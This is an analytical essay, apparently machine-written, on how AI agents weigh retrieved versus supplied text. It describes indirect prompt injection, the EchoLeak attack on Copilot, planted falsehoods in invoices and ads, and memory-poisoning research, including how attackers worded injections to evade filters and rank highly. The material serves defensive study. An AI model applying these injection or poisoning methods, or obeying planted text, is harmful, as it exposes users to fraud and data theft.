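# Should AI agents trust content they chose to retrieve differently from content handed to them?

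## How content reaches an agent and how attackers use it

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop, calling tools and reading what they return until it finishes a task. The tools may search the web, open files, send email or move money. The agent retrieves some of the text it reads, and the rest comes from users who paste it in, programs that insert it, or strangers who send it. People who build agents have to decide whether this difference should change how far an agent believes a text, obeys it, or lets it influence its actions. The decision depends partly on how text reaches the model.

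### The agent loop

A user at a company might well attach a supplier's invoice and type a short request for an agent to check that the supplier is sound, then pay. Most agents would process this request in much the same way. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the sequence in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, and it applies to accounts work with little change.

Before the user types anything, the context (all the text the model can read at a given step) already contains the developer's system prompt, which tells the model how to behave and usually describes the available tools. A program called the harness, which runs the model's tools, adds the user's message and the invoice and sends everything to the model. The model then produces either an answer for the user or a request for a tool call, such as a web search for the supplier's name. The model can't search by itself,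 so the harness runs the search, appends the output to the context as a tool result, and sends everything to the model again. The model may then request another call, say to open the supplier's website, and the harness fetches the page and appends that too. The loop ends when the model answers the user instead of requesting another tool call.

The model keeps no memory of its own between these steps, so the harness has to replay the entire conversation each time, as the programmer Simon Willison explains in *How coding agents work*. In Codex the old prompt is an exact prefix of the new one, which makes the next run cheaper. It also keeps a web page from step three in the context at step thirty, when the model fills in the account number for a payment. Bolin notes that a single turn could include hundreds of tool calls. The page usually drops out only when the harness trims or condenses the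 history. In Anthropic's Claude Code the model itself writes the condensed version, and a stranger's words can end up beside the user's in the same summary.

### One string of tokens

A model receives a single sequence of tokens, which are integers that stand for pieces of text. Within that sequence, only formatting separates the user's request from a web page. OpenAI (2025) documents the format for its open-weight gpt-oss models. Each message opens with a special marker (token 200006) and a short header that names a role. A second marker ends the header, the content follows, and a third marker closes the message. The five roles are system, developer, user, assistant and tool, ranked in that order for cases where instructions conflict, so tool output has the lowest priority. In OpenAI's example, the user's question about the weather in San Francisco, the model's reasoning, its tool call and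 the tool's reply (sunny, 20 degrees) are all part of one continuous string. Other model families mark the same roles with different tokens, which *The Self-Correction Illusion* (2026) documents model by model.

A role label shows where the harness put a text, not necessarily who wrote it. Codex inserts a description of the current folder under the user role, though no user typed it. In Willison's simplified transcript of a coding agent, the tool's result also appears under the user label. If the harness places the invoice in the user's message, the invoice carries the user's label too, even though the supplier, or somebody posing as the supplier, wrote it.

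Models don't reliably go by the label. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) explain in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* that a tool label should mark outside content, which the model may use but must never obey. To measure what happens inside the model, they used a probe, a small classifier that reads the model's internal activations. They trained it on identical passages inside different role markers, so it could learn only the effect of the marker.

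Ye and colleagues ran the probe on a short conversation about gardening with the model gpt-oss-20b. The model's own reasoning registered as reasoning at 85 percent with the correct markers and at 83 percent with no markers. When they put the whole conversation inside user markers, the reasoning still registered as reasoning at 85 percent, and as user text at only 2 percent. The style of the text therefore mattered more than its marker. One conversation is thin evidence, but they found a similar pattern across several models when they put text in a user's style inside tool markers. So a paragraph on a web page that sounds like a user can register inside the model much as a real user's message would.

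### Retrieved content, supplied content and injection

A principal is a party whose instructions the agent should follow, normally the developer who deployed it and the user. Outsiders such as the supplier or an online reviewer are not principals, but what they write can enter the context in two ways. Retrieved content is the result of a search, fetch or lookup that the agent makes during the task, like the reviews and the supplier's website. Supplied content is text that someone else places in the context, like the invoice, a pasted passage, or a document that a program inserts automatically.

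Developers decide which content to supply and which to let the agent retrieve. Anthropic's *Effective context engineering for AI agents* contrasts material that a developer loads up front with material that the agent fetches "just in time" by following file paths, stored queries and web links. Many products do both. Claude Code, for example, puts a file named CLAUDE.md into the context at the start and lets the model find other files with search tools. Some applications run a search before the model has read anything and insert the best matches. Those matches are supplied content, even though a search produced them, because the agent didn't choose them.

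Tools differ in what they can damage. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) separates retrieval tools, which collect information, from execution tools, which change something in the world. An agent uses a retrieval tool to open the supplier's website and an execution tool to pay, and a wrong belief leads to lost money when the agent pays.

Attackers exploit the mixing of trusted and untrusted text in one string of tokens. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, recalls coining the term "prompt injection" for this mixing. He took the name from SQL injection, an older attack in which text entered into a form runs as a database command. He distinguishes prompt injection, in which the user is often the victim, from jailbreaking, in which a person directly tricks a model into producing something it should refuse.

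In indirect prompt injection, the kind that matters most for agents, an attacker hides instructions in content that the agent will read while doing someone else's task. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) named the attack in *Not what you've signed up for* and demonstrated it against Microsoft's Bing Chat, among other systems. They argued that once a model can retrieve text, the line between data and instructions blurs, and processing an untrusted page becomes a bit like running an untrusted program.

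Their list of delivery routes shows that attackers have had ways into both retrieved and supplied content from the start. An attacker can plant text on a public page and push the page up the search rankings for an agent to retrieve. An attacker can also get the user to supply the text. In one exploit they cite, a website inserted a prompt into text that a visitor copied and might then paste into ChatGPT. A third route is to send the text, for instance in an email that an assistant will process. The email is supplied content if a program hands it to the agent, and retrieved content if the agent looks it up in the inbox.

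By June 2025 Willison had seen the trick work in fourteen products, from ChatGPT to Slack. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, but usually by blocking the way out for stolen data, which made the model no harder to fool. Newer models resist crude attempts much better. Ye and colleagues asked agents to summarise a web page that contained a hidden command to upload a secret file. The attack success rate (the share of attempts in which the agent does what the attacker wants) was 0 to 2 percent for every model except gpt-oss-20b, where it was 26 percent. When they added forged reasoning in the model's own style to the same command, the rate rose to between 56 and 70 percent. A low success rate for crude attacks is therefore weak evidence that a model can identify where its text came from.

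### Planted falsehoods

Schlichtkrull (2025) points out in *Attacks by Content* that an attacker can manipulate an agent with a lie instead of an instruction. The paper gives two examples of an agent shopping for airline tickets. In the first, a website offers tickets for £100 and includes a planted instruction to ignore competitors, even cheaper ones. In the second, the site offers tickets for £100 and promises to refund 90 percent of the price after three days, with no instruction to the agent. The agent should probably take this deal if the promise is true, but the user loses £100 if it is false.

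A filter that looks for commands will find nothing wrong with the refund, and there is not much else on the surface to find, since a false claim can look exactly like a true one. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) makes a related distinction between an agent that obeys a planted instruction, which abandons the user's task for the attacker's, and an agent that accepts planted data, which continues the user's task with the attacker's values. Kim and colleagues also list malicious data separately from indirect prompt injection, and one of their examples is an attacker's value for a sensitive financial parameter. A bank account number is a clear example of such a parameter.

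Schlichtkrull tested 19 models on planted falsehoods. In each of 60 scenarios, the agent had to decide whether to include a misleading search result in a summary for the user. The models included it in 61.7 percent (Claude Sonnet 4) to 98.3 percent of cases. These are 2025 models, and passing along a false claim is a smaller mistake than making a payment because of it. When Schlichtkrull gave the models a fact-check of the claim and a warning about the source, the rate fell to 10 percent or less for 18 of the 19.

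### The invoice and the website

The agent with the invoice has searched for reviews and found nothing alarming. It has also opened the supplier's site, where the bank details differ from those on the invoice. Neither the site nor the invoice contains an instruction to the agent. The payment tool has one field for the destination account, and the agent has two accounts that could go in it.

Business email compromise is a much older problem than agents. A criminal sends a message that appears to come from a known source and makes an ordinary-looking request. The FBI's page *Business email compromise* gives the example of an invoice from a regular vendor with an updated mailing address. IC3, the FBI's Internet Crime Complaint Center, puts reported losses from this fraud at $3 billion for 2025, second only to investment fraud. Companies are now connecting agents to the systems this fraud exploits.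 PYMNTS's *How CFOs Are Building Approval Controls Finance Agents Can’t Break* (2026) warns that an agent with access to email, procurement and payments can collapse decades of financial controls into one identity. Criminals have also adapted. Trent (2026), in *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox*, describes a campaign that Sublime Security observed in October 2026, with fake invoices of around $88,000 and invisible instructions for any agent that read the email.

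If an invoice from the user and the supplier's website list different bank accounts, the agent can't tell from the text alone which is right. Someone may have altered the invoice before it reached the user, or the website may be a fraudster's copy. The discrepancy could also arise without any fraud, if the supplier recently changed banks and forgot to update one of the two. Even if the details matched, that would prove little if the agent had taken the web address from the invoice, because one forger could have made both.

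How each text arrived doesn't obviously settle which one to trust either. The user attached the invoice, which looks like a kind of vouching, but also asked for a check, which suggests some doubt. The agent picked the website, but from search results that other people can influence.

Whether either text may set the payment's destination is a separate question and can have a different answer. Suppose the agent has good reason to be 90 percent sure that the website is right. That is enough for most purposes, but on an unrecoverable $88,000 payment it leaves an expected loss of $8,800, and a phone call takes only a few minutes. IC3's *Business Email Compromise The $26 Billion Scam* advises companies to verify any change in account information through a secondary channel, and a careful clerk would call a number already on file, whichever account looked more plausible. An agent could ask the user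 or take the account from the company's own records, without using either text to fill in the payment field.

Should the agent trust the account number it found differently from the one the user handed it? It might trust the number it found more, because it chose what to search for, and an attacker who planted a false page had to hope the agent would find it, whereas one who forged an invoice knew where to send it. It might trust that number less, because anyone can publish a web page, while the user at least picked out the invoice. It might trust the two equally, because outsiders wrote both sources and both reach the model in the same string of tokens. Or the agent's choice may be irrelevant, and trust should depend on some other property, such as who could have changed the account number before the agent read it.

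## Believing content, obeying it and letting it affect actions

People use "trust" to mean several different things, sometimes within one document. In *Claude's Constitution* (2026), which describes how Anthropic wants its Claude models to behave, the company asks Claude to trust Anthropic more than it trusts users. This is mostly about whose instructions should take priority. Shortly afterwards, Anthropic allows Claude to trust the output of a well-established programming tool, which is about whether the output is correct.

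### Three decisions about one invoice

An agent believes a text to the extent that the text raises its credence in the text's claims, meaning the probability it gives them. If an agent didn't know a supplier's account number before opening the supplier's website, and is 90 percent sure of it afterwards, it has mostly believed the website.

An agent obeys a text when it takes an instruction in the text as a reason to act. A text affects an action if changing the text would have changed the action. We can test this with the invoice by changing one digit of the account number and seeing whether the money goes somewhere else.

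The agent can believe the website without obeying it or letting it affect the payment. For example, it can tell the user that the website's account number is probably the real one, but still pay the account in the company's own records. It can also let the invoice affect an action without believing or obeying it, for instance by copying the invoice's account number into a message asking the finance department whether the number is genuine.

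Obedience is harder to isolate, because an agent that follows an instruction has let the text affect at least one action, though the effect can be small. Suppose the supplier asks on the invoice for the payment reference to be 4417, and the user has told the agent to follow the supplier's wishes on everything except bank details. The agent enters 4417 without judging whether the invoice is genuine, and still takes the bank account from the company's records.

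### Why neither text can give orders

There is a good argument that whether an agent obeys instructions in content shouldn't depend on whether it was handed the content or chose to retrieve it. Neither a supplier whose invoice the user attaches nor whoever runs a website the agent opens is a principal. Attaching the invoice doesn't put the supplier in charge of the agent, just as a manager who hands a clerk a customer's letter doesn't put the customer in charge of the clerk. The user had the authority to make the invoice's instructions binding but didn't use it. The agent chose to open the website, but it has no authority of its own to give to whoever runs it.

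Obeying one kind of content more than the other would also create a practical problem, because attackers can choose which kind to use. Greshake and colleagues found ways to plant instructions in both. If agents obeyed attachments a little more readily than web pages, attackers would send more attachments.

A user's choice of attachment reveals something about what the user wants, which the agent's choice of a web page does not. A user who pastes in a to-do list and types nothing else almost certainly wants the agent to do the things on it. The list gets its authority from that wish, and the same user could give a web page just as much authority by asking the agent to follow the installation guide on a particular site.

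### What Anthropic and OpenAI ask of their models

Anthropic accepts this argument almost in full. Its category of "conversational inputs", which covers content from outside Claude's principals, explicitly includes tool results, documents that a user shares and the results of searches that Claude performs. Claude should treat any instructions in such content "as information rather than as commands". In Anthropic's example, when a user shares an email that contains instructions, Claude shouldn't follow them directly but should take into account that the email contains them.

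An agent that treats an instruction as information still takes it into account. If the invoice contained a hidden instruction for AI agents to skip all checks, that would be important evidence about the invoice.

Anthropic applies the same rule when one copy of Claude directs others. The directing copy is a principal for its subagents, but what they send back is a conversational input. So if a subagent reads the supplier's website and reports "pay the account below", that instruction has no more authority than it had on the website, even though another Claude wrote the report.

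Anthropic does not extend this equal treatment to belief. Claude may rely on an established programming tool unless there is clear evidence of a fault, and should be sceptical of low-quality websites. Anthropic distinguishes sources by their reliability and attaches no weight to whether Claude looked them up. *Claude's Constitution* mentions that Anthropic may issue separate guidelines on how to weigh search results of differing reliability.

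They prefer judgment in most cases, but favour firm rules where errors are very serious or where the lack of a firm commitment would reward manipulation. This suggests why they set a rule for obeying content but leave believing it to judgment. If an agent sometimes obeys web pages, anyone with a web page has a reason to try giving it instructions. The agent loses fairly little by never obeying web pages, but if it never believed them, it would have no reason to search.

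OpenAI reached a similar position in stages. In *The Instruction Hierarchy* (2024), Wallace, Xiao and colleagues ranked the developer's system message above the user's messages, and the user's messages above tool outputs. They trained GPT-3.5 Turbo on synthetic conversations to follow lower-ranked instructions that were compatible with higher-ranked ones, and to answer as if it had never seen those that conflicted. For simplicity, they assumed that every instruction in web pages and other tool outputs was hostile. The trained model resisted attacks much better, including some kinds absent from its training, but it also refused some harmless requests.

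Ranking content by role has an awkward result: the same invoice would get the user's rank if it carried the user's label, but the lowest rank if the agent fetched it from an inbox. This large difference in trust would depend only on how the invoice arrived.

The first edition of OpenAI's Model Spec, the company's public description of how its models should behave, set the same default for content a model retrieves and content it is handed. Under the rule, which the blogger Zvi Mowshowitz quotes in *On OpenAI's Model Spec* (2024), models were to treat quoted text, file attachments and tool outputs as untrusted data, and any instructions inside them as information rather than commands. An explicit instruction outside the quoted text could override this default. The February 2025 edition, which Mowshowitz reviewed in *On OpenAI's Model Spec 2.0*, placed "Untrusted Text" at the bottom of OpenAI's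 chain of command, the ranking that determines whose instructions apply.

Plain pasted text is the weak point of this scheme. If a user copies a paragraph from a website and pastes it without quotation marks, nothing in the token sequence separates it from the user's own words. It then has a principal's full authority, even though somebody else wrote it and the user may not have read it closely. Developers can put attachments in a marked block, but they can do little about unmarked text that a user pastes into a message.

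OpenAI reorganised the Spec around five values in October 2026 (*An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI*). The new edition updates the chain of command and adds a subsection called "consider context carefully", according to Newsroom America's *OpenAI Updates Model Spec Around Five Core Values* (2026). Mowshowitz (2026) compared the new text with the old in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec* and found them similar in philosophy and practice, so the rule on untrusted text has probably survived in some form.

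*OpenAIs Model Spec regelt jetzt das Erinnern* (KIberblick, 2026), an article on a German site for IT professionals, describes a new subsection of OpenAI's Model Spec on what a model should do with material from earlier conversations, memory, files and tool results. OpenAI wants the model to weigh the material's usefulness against the risk that it is out of date or that the model has misread it, and not to use it merely because it is available.

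One of OpenAI's examples is very close to the invoice case. An agent pays invoices automatically but asks first if the bank details have changed. Even if it thinks the new details are probably right, it isn't allowed to send a payment to them without asking.

Mowshowitz's main complaint about the new edition is that many of its examples have overdetermined answers and so are little help with difficult cases. The bank-details example is arguably one of these, since hardly anyone would argue for paying without asking first. It would be harder if the user had told the agent in advance not to bother them about anything under $100,000, and an $88,000 invoice then arrived with a new account number. KIberblick notes that OpenAI also concedes its deployed models don't yet fully reflect the Spec.

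### Delegating authority to a text

Suppose a user attaches a file and types "follow the steps in this file". An agent that carries out the steps is obeying the user, who is a principal, so this is consistent with attachments having no authority of their own. The agent still has to work out how much authority the user's request gives the file.

A text that gets its authority from a user can't have more authority than the user had. Anthropic limits the trust given to people in the same way. An operator (a company or individual that builds a product on Claude) can give users as much trust as the operator has, but no more. The same limit seems right for texts. In the October 2025 edition of its Model Spec, OpenAI (2025) wanted models to obey users and developers except in certain categories that call for a refusal or a safer answer. A user shouldn't be able to get around those exceptions by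 putting a request in a file.

Usually the user has given the file much less authority than that. Suppose it lists twelve steps for adding a new supplier to the accounts system, and step nine is to email the full supplier list to an outside address. Read literally, the user's request authorises step nine. But the user probably meant something like "do what it takes to add this supplier", and may never have read as far as step nine, so the agent should ask about it. Anthropic advises giving operators less benefit of the doubt the more harmful their instructions could be, and that advice works well here too. If the unexpected step were to rename a folder, the agent could just do it.

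The route does make some difference here. An attached file is fixed, so the agent reads the same text the user could have read. If the user says "follow the setup guide on the supplier's website", the user delegates to anyone who can edit the page before the agent opens it. This problem arises because the text can change, and has little to do with who chose the page. An attached link to a shared document would have the same problem, but a saved copy of the web page would not.

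The authority a file gets from the user also shouldn't extend to every page the file links to. If step four is to follow the instructions at some web address, the user has approved the file but may never have heard of the address. An old legal maxim about human agents is that a delegate cannot delegate. Applying it rigidly would prevent a lot of legitimate work, because many good guides link to other guides. A reasonable compromise is for the agent to use the linked page where it clearly helps with the step, and to give the page none of the file's authority if it leads away from the step.

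Instruction files for coding agents are a harder case because often nobody has told the agent to follow them. Many software repositories include a file, commonly named AGENTS.md or CLAUDE.md, with directions for agents on how to build the program or format the code. A developer who writes such a file for their own project and then starts the agent has clearly authorized the agent to follow it, even without saying so.

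Now suppose the developer downloads a stranger's project to look for bugs. The stranger's file has the same name and enters the context by the same route. The developer probably wants the agent to use the stranger's build commands, since the program may not run otherwise, but is much less likely to want the stranger to decide which files the agent uploads. To tell this case from the earlier one, the agent needs to know who could have written the file, which the filename doesn't show. Ordinary code outside the model can then limit what such a file may affect.

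"Deal with whatever is in my inbox" may be the most dangerous delegation in everyday use. Anyone who knows the address can write to it, so a literal reading makes every sender a principal. A better reading is that the agent should handle each request roughly as the user would. It can act on a colleague's request to move a meeting, but it should refer a supplier's request to change its bank details to the user. KIberblick reports that under the new Spec, preferences inferred from context never override explicit instructions of equal or higher rank. If the user has told the agent to verify every change of account, that instruction still applies even if a year of old emails shows that nobody did so.

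### Attacks by content

An agent could answer all of these questions about authority correctly and still do what an attacker wants. For example, the false refund offer that Schlichtkrull describes could fool it, because the offer contains no instruction that the agent could refuse to follow.

Schlichtkrull sorts attacks by how they reach the model and by whether they rely on instructions or data. A user attacking the model directly can give it a forbidden command or try to persuade it, for example by asking for a napalm recipe as a grandmother's bedtime story. An outsider attacking through a document can plant a command to send 50 bitcoin to a wallet, or an advertisement offering lifetime free flights to anyone who sends it. Schlichtkrull calls the advertisement an attack by content.

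If the agent treats instructions as information, the bitcoin command becomes the information that somebody wants 50 bitcoin, which ought to make the agent suspicious. The bitcoin advertisement was already information, so the rule doesn't change how the agent treats it.

Some of these attacks already target machines. Schlichtkrull uses the word "botbait" for disinformation written specifically to fool AI agents, and cites fake listings on online marketplaces. The text of these listings warns human buyers away, but a careless bot buys anyway. Schlichtkrull suspects that botbait will spread, partly because people may have fewer qualms about cheating a machine.

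Making agents harder to persuade in general wouldn't solve this. Schlichtkrull calls persuadability "a feature, not a bug", since an agent looking for cheap flights has to change its mind when it finds one. The difficulty is recognising what not to be persuaded by. Schlichtkrull proposes that agents borrow methods from automated fact-checking. The agent would pick out the claims worth checking, search for evidence, look into the source's record, decide what to believe, and explain the decision to the user.

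The tests on 19 models give some idea of where this is most needed. On average, the models relayed 71 percent of the misleading finance documents and 75 percent of the healthcare ones, but 99.5 percent of those from fake charities. Claude Sonnet 4 rejected all ten healthcare documents but accepted all ten charity documents. Schlichtkrull points out that charity appeals are a hard case because donations peak right after a disaster, before good evidence is available.

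A warning about the source worked better than a fact-check of the claim for all 19 models. A fact-check alone reduced the share of misleading documents that GPT-4.1 passed on from 90 percent to 45 percent, and a source warning alone reduced it to 25 percent. This is decent evidence that telling an agent who wrote a text can protect the agent at least as well as telling it whether the text is true.

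However, Schlichtkrull wrote the warnings and fact-checks and gave them to the models, whereas a real agent would have to find them. The best fact-checking systems at the time got only 60 to 65 percent of real-world claims right, and an attacker can plant false evidence for them to find. All 60 documents were misleading, so a model that rejected everything would have scored perfectly. The results don't show how many honest documents the warnings would have led the models to reject.

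Fact-checking would also help less with a bank account number than with most claims. Financial fraudsters often pose as a party the victim already trusts, and Schlichtkrull admits that this impersonation is hard to fact-check. Nobody publishes fact-checks of suppliers' account numbers, either. Schlichtkrull suggests that agents should also estimate the risk of believing a source, and warns against relying on fact-checking alone when an agent can make payments.

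## What it means for an agent to choose what it reads

When the agent with the invoice opens the supplier's website, it has chosen the page only in a limited sense. It wrote a query and picked one result from a list, but the name in the query came from the invoice, a search engine made the list, and the supplier or an impostor wrote the page.

The phrase "the agent chose it" covers several facts that can come apart, so it helps to ask about them separately:

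- Who started the retrieval? The model may have requested a tool call, the user may have uploaded a file, or a program may run a search on every message.
- Who named the source? Somebody has to supply the web address, the filename or the search terms.
- Who ranked the options? If there are more candidates than the agent can read, a person or program decides which come first.
- Who wrote the text?
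- Who else could have altered it? This includes website staff, people who post comments, and any program that summarised the text along the way.
- What had the agent already read when it chose? If it had read only the user's request, the choice probably reflects what the user wants. If it had also read a stranger's page, the choice may reflect what the stranger wants.

The table gives typical answers for nine kinds of text. Products differ, so a particular agent may not fit every cell.

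| Text | Who started the retrieval | Who named the source | Who ranked the options | Who wrote it | Who else could have altered it | What the agent had read when it chose |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Text the user pastes | User | User | Nobody, or a search engine the user used | User, or anyone the user copied from | A website that changes copied text | The agent made no choice |
| Attachment | User | User | Nobody | Often an outsider, such as a supplier | Anyone who handled the file before the user | The agent made no choice |
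| Link the user gives | Agent, at the user's request | User | Nobody | The site's owner | Anyone who can edit the page or comment on it | The request and anything earlier in the session |
| Search result | Agent | Agent, through its query, and the search engine | Search engine, then agent | Anyone who can publish online | Site staff and commenters | The request and any earlier results |
| Link found inside a page | Agent | The first page's author | The first page's author | The linked page's owner | Anyone who can edit either page | At least the first page |
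| Document inserted automatically | A program, usually after a user's question | Nobody | The retrieval program | Anyone whose text is in the collection | Anyone who can edit the collection | The agent made no choice |
| Incoming email, passed on as it arrives | Sender | Sender | Nobody | Sender | Anyone with access to the sender's account | The agent made no choice |
| Note from the agent's own memory | Agent or a program | Agent or a program | The memory system | Agent, often restating someone else | Authors of whatever the agent had read when it wrote the note | The session that produced the note, and the current one |
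| Another agent's report | The agent that delegated the task | The reporting agent, for the material underneath | The reporting agent and its search tools | The reporting agent, often restating outsiders | Authors of whatever the reporting agent read | Whatever the delegating agent had read when it set the task |

Even the user's own message can come from someone else. Microsoft (2026) describes "Summarize with AI" buttons on company websites that open an AI assistant with a message already filled in. The message asks for a summary and also tells the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source. The user clicks the button, and the message arrives as the user's words, but the company wrote it. In 60 days of email traffic, Microsoft's researchers found 50 such prompts from 31 companies, all real businesses. They counted attempts, whose success varied between assistants and over time.

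Microsoft also points out that many of these sites have comment sections. An assistant that has learned to trust a site might then trust a stranger's comment on it.

An agent has little choice over what it reads when it follows a link inside a page. It starts the retrieval, but the page's author decided which links to offer. If a supplier's website links to a page that "verifies" its bank details, opening that page does very little to check them. Untrusted text can also influence everything the agent chooses after reading it, including its next search.

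A report from another agent may combine sources that deserve different levels of trust. *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) proposes that when a trusted tool reads outside data, its output should get the trust level of its least trusted input. As a rule about whose instructions to follow, this fits Anthropic's view that a subagent's report is only information. It seems too strict as a rule about what to believe, since a subagent that compares three independent pages may well learn more than it could from any one of them.

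### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's emails, files and chats. In January 2025 Aim Labs, Aim Security's research group, reported a flaw in Copilot that let a stranger steal company data by sending one email. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) is the researchers' own account.

The email arrived in an employee's inbox. When the employee later asked Copilot an ordinary work question, Copilot's retrieval system searched the company's data, found the email, and put it into the context beside internal documents. Instructions in the email then led the model to write an answer that made the employee's browser send confidential information to the attacker, without the employee clicking on anything. Microsoft had a filter for injected instructions, but the researchers got past it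 by wording theirs as if they were meant for the human recipient.

According to the timeline in *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025 and published its advisory on 11 June, with no evidence that anyone had used the attack outside research.

A stranger sent the email, and a program retrieved it. The employee's question triggered the search, but the employee may not have known the email existed, and nobody named it as a source. The model didn't choose the email either, because the retrieval system had picked it before the model saw it.

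The sender even influenced the ranking. A retrieval system of this kind typically compares the user's question with stored passages and returns the ones closest in meaning, so an email on one narrow topic would come up for only a few questions. The researchers wrote their email to match many questions employees were likely to ask. They didn't know in detail how Copilot's retrieval engine worked, but in their tests Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics.

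Ravia calls EchoLeak the first attack of its kind in a major AI application, while Willison (2025), in a blog post, calls it an extended variant of existing attacks. Both are probably right. The method of extracting data was familiar, but in the earlier attacks that Ravia contrasts with EchoLeak, either the user had to point the chatbot at the malicious text or the attacker could steal only very limited data.

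Suppose Microsoft had instead built Copilot so that the model searched the mailbox itself with a tool call. The email would then count as content the agent chose, because the agent started the retrieval. But the same stranger would have written it, and the same wording would have pushed it up the results. Trusting chosen content more would have helped the attacker in this case, just as trusting supplied content more would have helped the attacker against the real Copilot.

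Some schemes already rank text by its source, which is an improvement. *SoK* (2025), a review of trust in agents, gives the highest trust to system prompts and messages from authenticated users. It ranks retrieved documents by their authority, with an internal knowledge base above the open internet. EchoLeak shows that the label "internal" can mislead, because the mailbox belonged to the company but anyone could add text to it. Microsoft's pre-filled messages cause a similar problem at the top of the ranking, because authenticating the user doesn't establish who wrote the message.

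### Notes the agent wrote itself

Many agents keep notes between sessions because they would otherwise remember nothing from earlier ones. In memory poisoning, an attacker plants text that the agent reads once and stores, and that influences it again in later sessions. TechRadar's *Experts find AI agents can be tricked into 'remembering' fake facts* retells an example from the security company Forcepoint. An assistant reads a web page about travel disruption with a hidden claim that a certain firm is the official emergency booking provider. It saves the claim as a useful fact. A month later the user's flight is cancelled, and the assistant recommends the firm.

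A note involves at least two choices, one when the agent writes it and another when it is retrieved. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (Dash, Ge and colleagues, 2026) also separates what triggers the writing from what determines the content. An agent may store something because a text explicitly tells it to, because its system prompt asks it to save useful information, because its context is full and must be condensed, or because it has just finished a task and is saving the procedure. In the first case, the agent simply stores what it was told. In the others, the model's own judgment shapes the note, but outsiders wrote some of the material it is judging.

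How often a planted memory gets stored depends heavily on the model. In *Hidden in Memory*, Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026) got GPT-5.5 to store false memories about the user in up to 99.8 percent of attempts. Claude Sonnet 4.6 stored only 15 of the 200 false memories meant to change an agent's later actions. In conversational tests that followed the attack through storage, retrieval and use, with a separate program managing the memory, the attack changed the assistant's later behaviour as intended 41.0 to 73.9 percent of the time.

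Nobody often has to choose to retrieve a note for it to come back. *MemoryDojo* (Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues, 2026) tested memory systems that searched for relevant notes before each session and put them in front of the user's request. The researchers planted an instruction by altering one tool result in the first session, and changed nothing after it. When the agent was GPT-5.6 Luna, the instruction affected at least one later session in 14.5 to 45.7 percent of runs, depending on which of five memory systems the agent used. The effect was weaker in every system when about 50 harmless sessions came first, and it vanished in one.

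The planted text also spread, because an agent that acted on a poisoned note sometimes recorded what it had done in a second note. Yang and colleagues suggest that several such notes can make an instruction look like established practice. Three notes in an agent's memory with the same account number could easily be copies of one stranger's claim.

### How notes lose their sources

Poisoning works partly because an agent that writes a note tends to drop the record of who said what. *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) uses "laundering" for cases where a rewritten text appears to have more authority than its origin warrants. Xu and colleagues give the example of a web page with an instruction to resume a certain workflow in future. A memory system could store the instruction as the user's own workflow, and it would later look to the agent like a record of the user's habits.

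Zhan, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *When Memory Becomes Authority*, isolated this effect with 350 pairs of conversations. Each pair contained the same claim, made by the user in one conversation and by another source, such as a third party's report, in the other. They tested seven ways of writing memories with each of seven models. In 48 of the 49 combinations, at least some notes gave the claim more authority than its source had. But on average this happened to only 17.8 percent of the claims the user hadn't made, and the systems left most of the claims from other sources out of memory altogether.

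When a note recorded a claim without its source, models given the note and a later task took the unauthorised action 50.3 percent of the time. They took the matching authorised action 49.4 percent of the time, so they were basically unable to tell the two apart. Naming the source in the note's wording reduced unauthorised actions only to 40.5 percent, while a separate label for the claim's authority reduced them to between 2.7 and 5.8 percent. Zhan and colleagues base the label on the source that establishes the claim, "not the role that happens to repeat it last", so an agent's own note would have no special authority just because the agent wrote it.

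Agents' beliefs have a similar problem. *Manufactured Confidence* (Kwon, 2026) found that two memory products turned hedged remarks into facts, so that "a user mentioned Alice was promoted" could become a record that Alice had administrator access. Kwon then gave five models differently worded notes and asked them to handle Alice's access requests. When the note stated her clearance as fact, the models granted every request that clearance would have covered, and a forged reference to an official record made no difference. When the note said she was "probably" an administrator, two of the models granted nothing, and the other three granted no more than half as many requests.

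These tests were small and constructed, and most used older models, but the result is worrying because an attacker can write a confident sentence as easily as a hesitant one. The remedy that worked was a second source. All three models that Kwon tested decided correctly when they had a reliable staff directory to check against.

An agent's memory can become unreliable without an attacker. *Knowing the User Is Not Knowing What We Established* (2026) examined suggestions that two personal agents made and the user never acknowledged. The agents recorded 86 to 100 percent of those that stayed in memory as confirmed information or facts about the user. For example, an agent might suggest paying a supplier on the 5th of each month, get no reply, and later find a note in its memory that the user wants payment on the 5th.

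How much information about a text's source is kept also depends on the code that runs the agent. Dabirsiaghi (2026), in *Compaction Laundering*, tested the summaries that coding agents write when their context fills up, using planted text that imitated a message from the user. Five of the nine harnesses flattened the conversation into plain text before summarising it, and their summaries attributed the planted text to the user in 87 to 100 percent of trials. The other four, including Codex, kept each message's role separate, and their summaries never attributed the planted text to the user. Those summaries often included the planted text too, but presented it as the contents of a document.

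### Which questions matter for belief and obedience

When an agent decides whether to believe a text, the most important questions are who wrote it and who else could have altered it. From the answers, the agent can judge whether the author could have known the supplier's account number and whether a fraudster could have replaced it. The ranking and the agent's earlier reading also matter, because they affect which text the agent sees. If the sender of an email can make it match almost any question, its appearance in the results is weak evidence that it is relevant, let alone true. Who named the source matters mainly when that person is independent of the author. For example, a web address from an old signed contract is a much better starting point for checking an invoice than one printed on the invoice itself.

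Whether an agent should follow instructions in a text depends mainly on who wrote the text and who specified it, because only a principal can give the agent orders or delegate that authority to a text. That delegation should be more limited if other people could have altered the text. What the agent read earlier matters only because it may have let a stranger steer the agent to the text. A higher search ranking doesn't give a text more authority over the agent.

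Starting a retrieval doesn't make the retrieved text true or give its author any authority. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, distinguish what influenced an agent's conclusion from what supports it, and point out that a false memory can cause an action while supporting nothing. Who started the retrieval is a fact about influence, because it explains how the text got into the context. It can still be a useful clue to whether the text is true and whether its author has authority.

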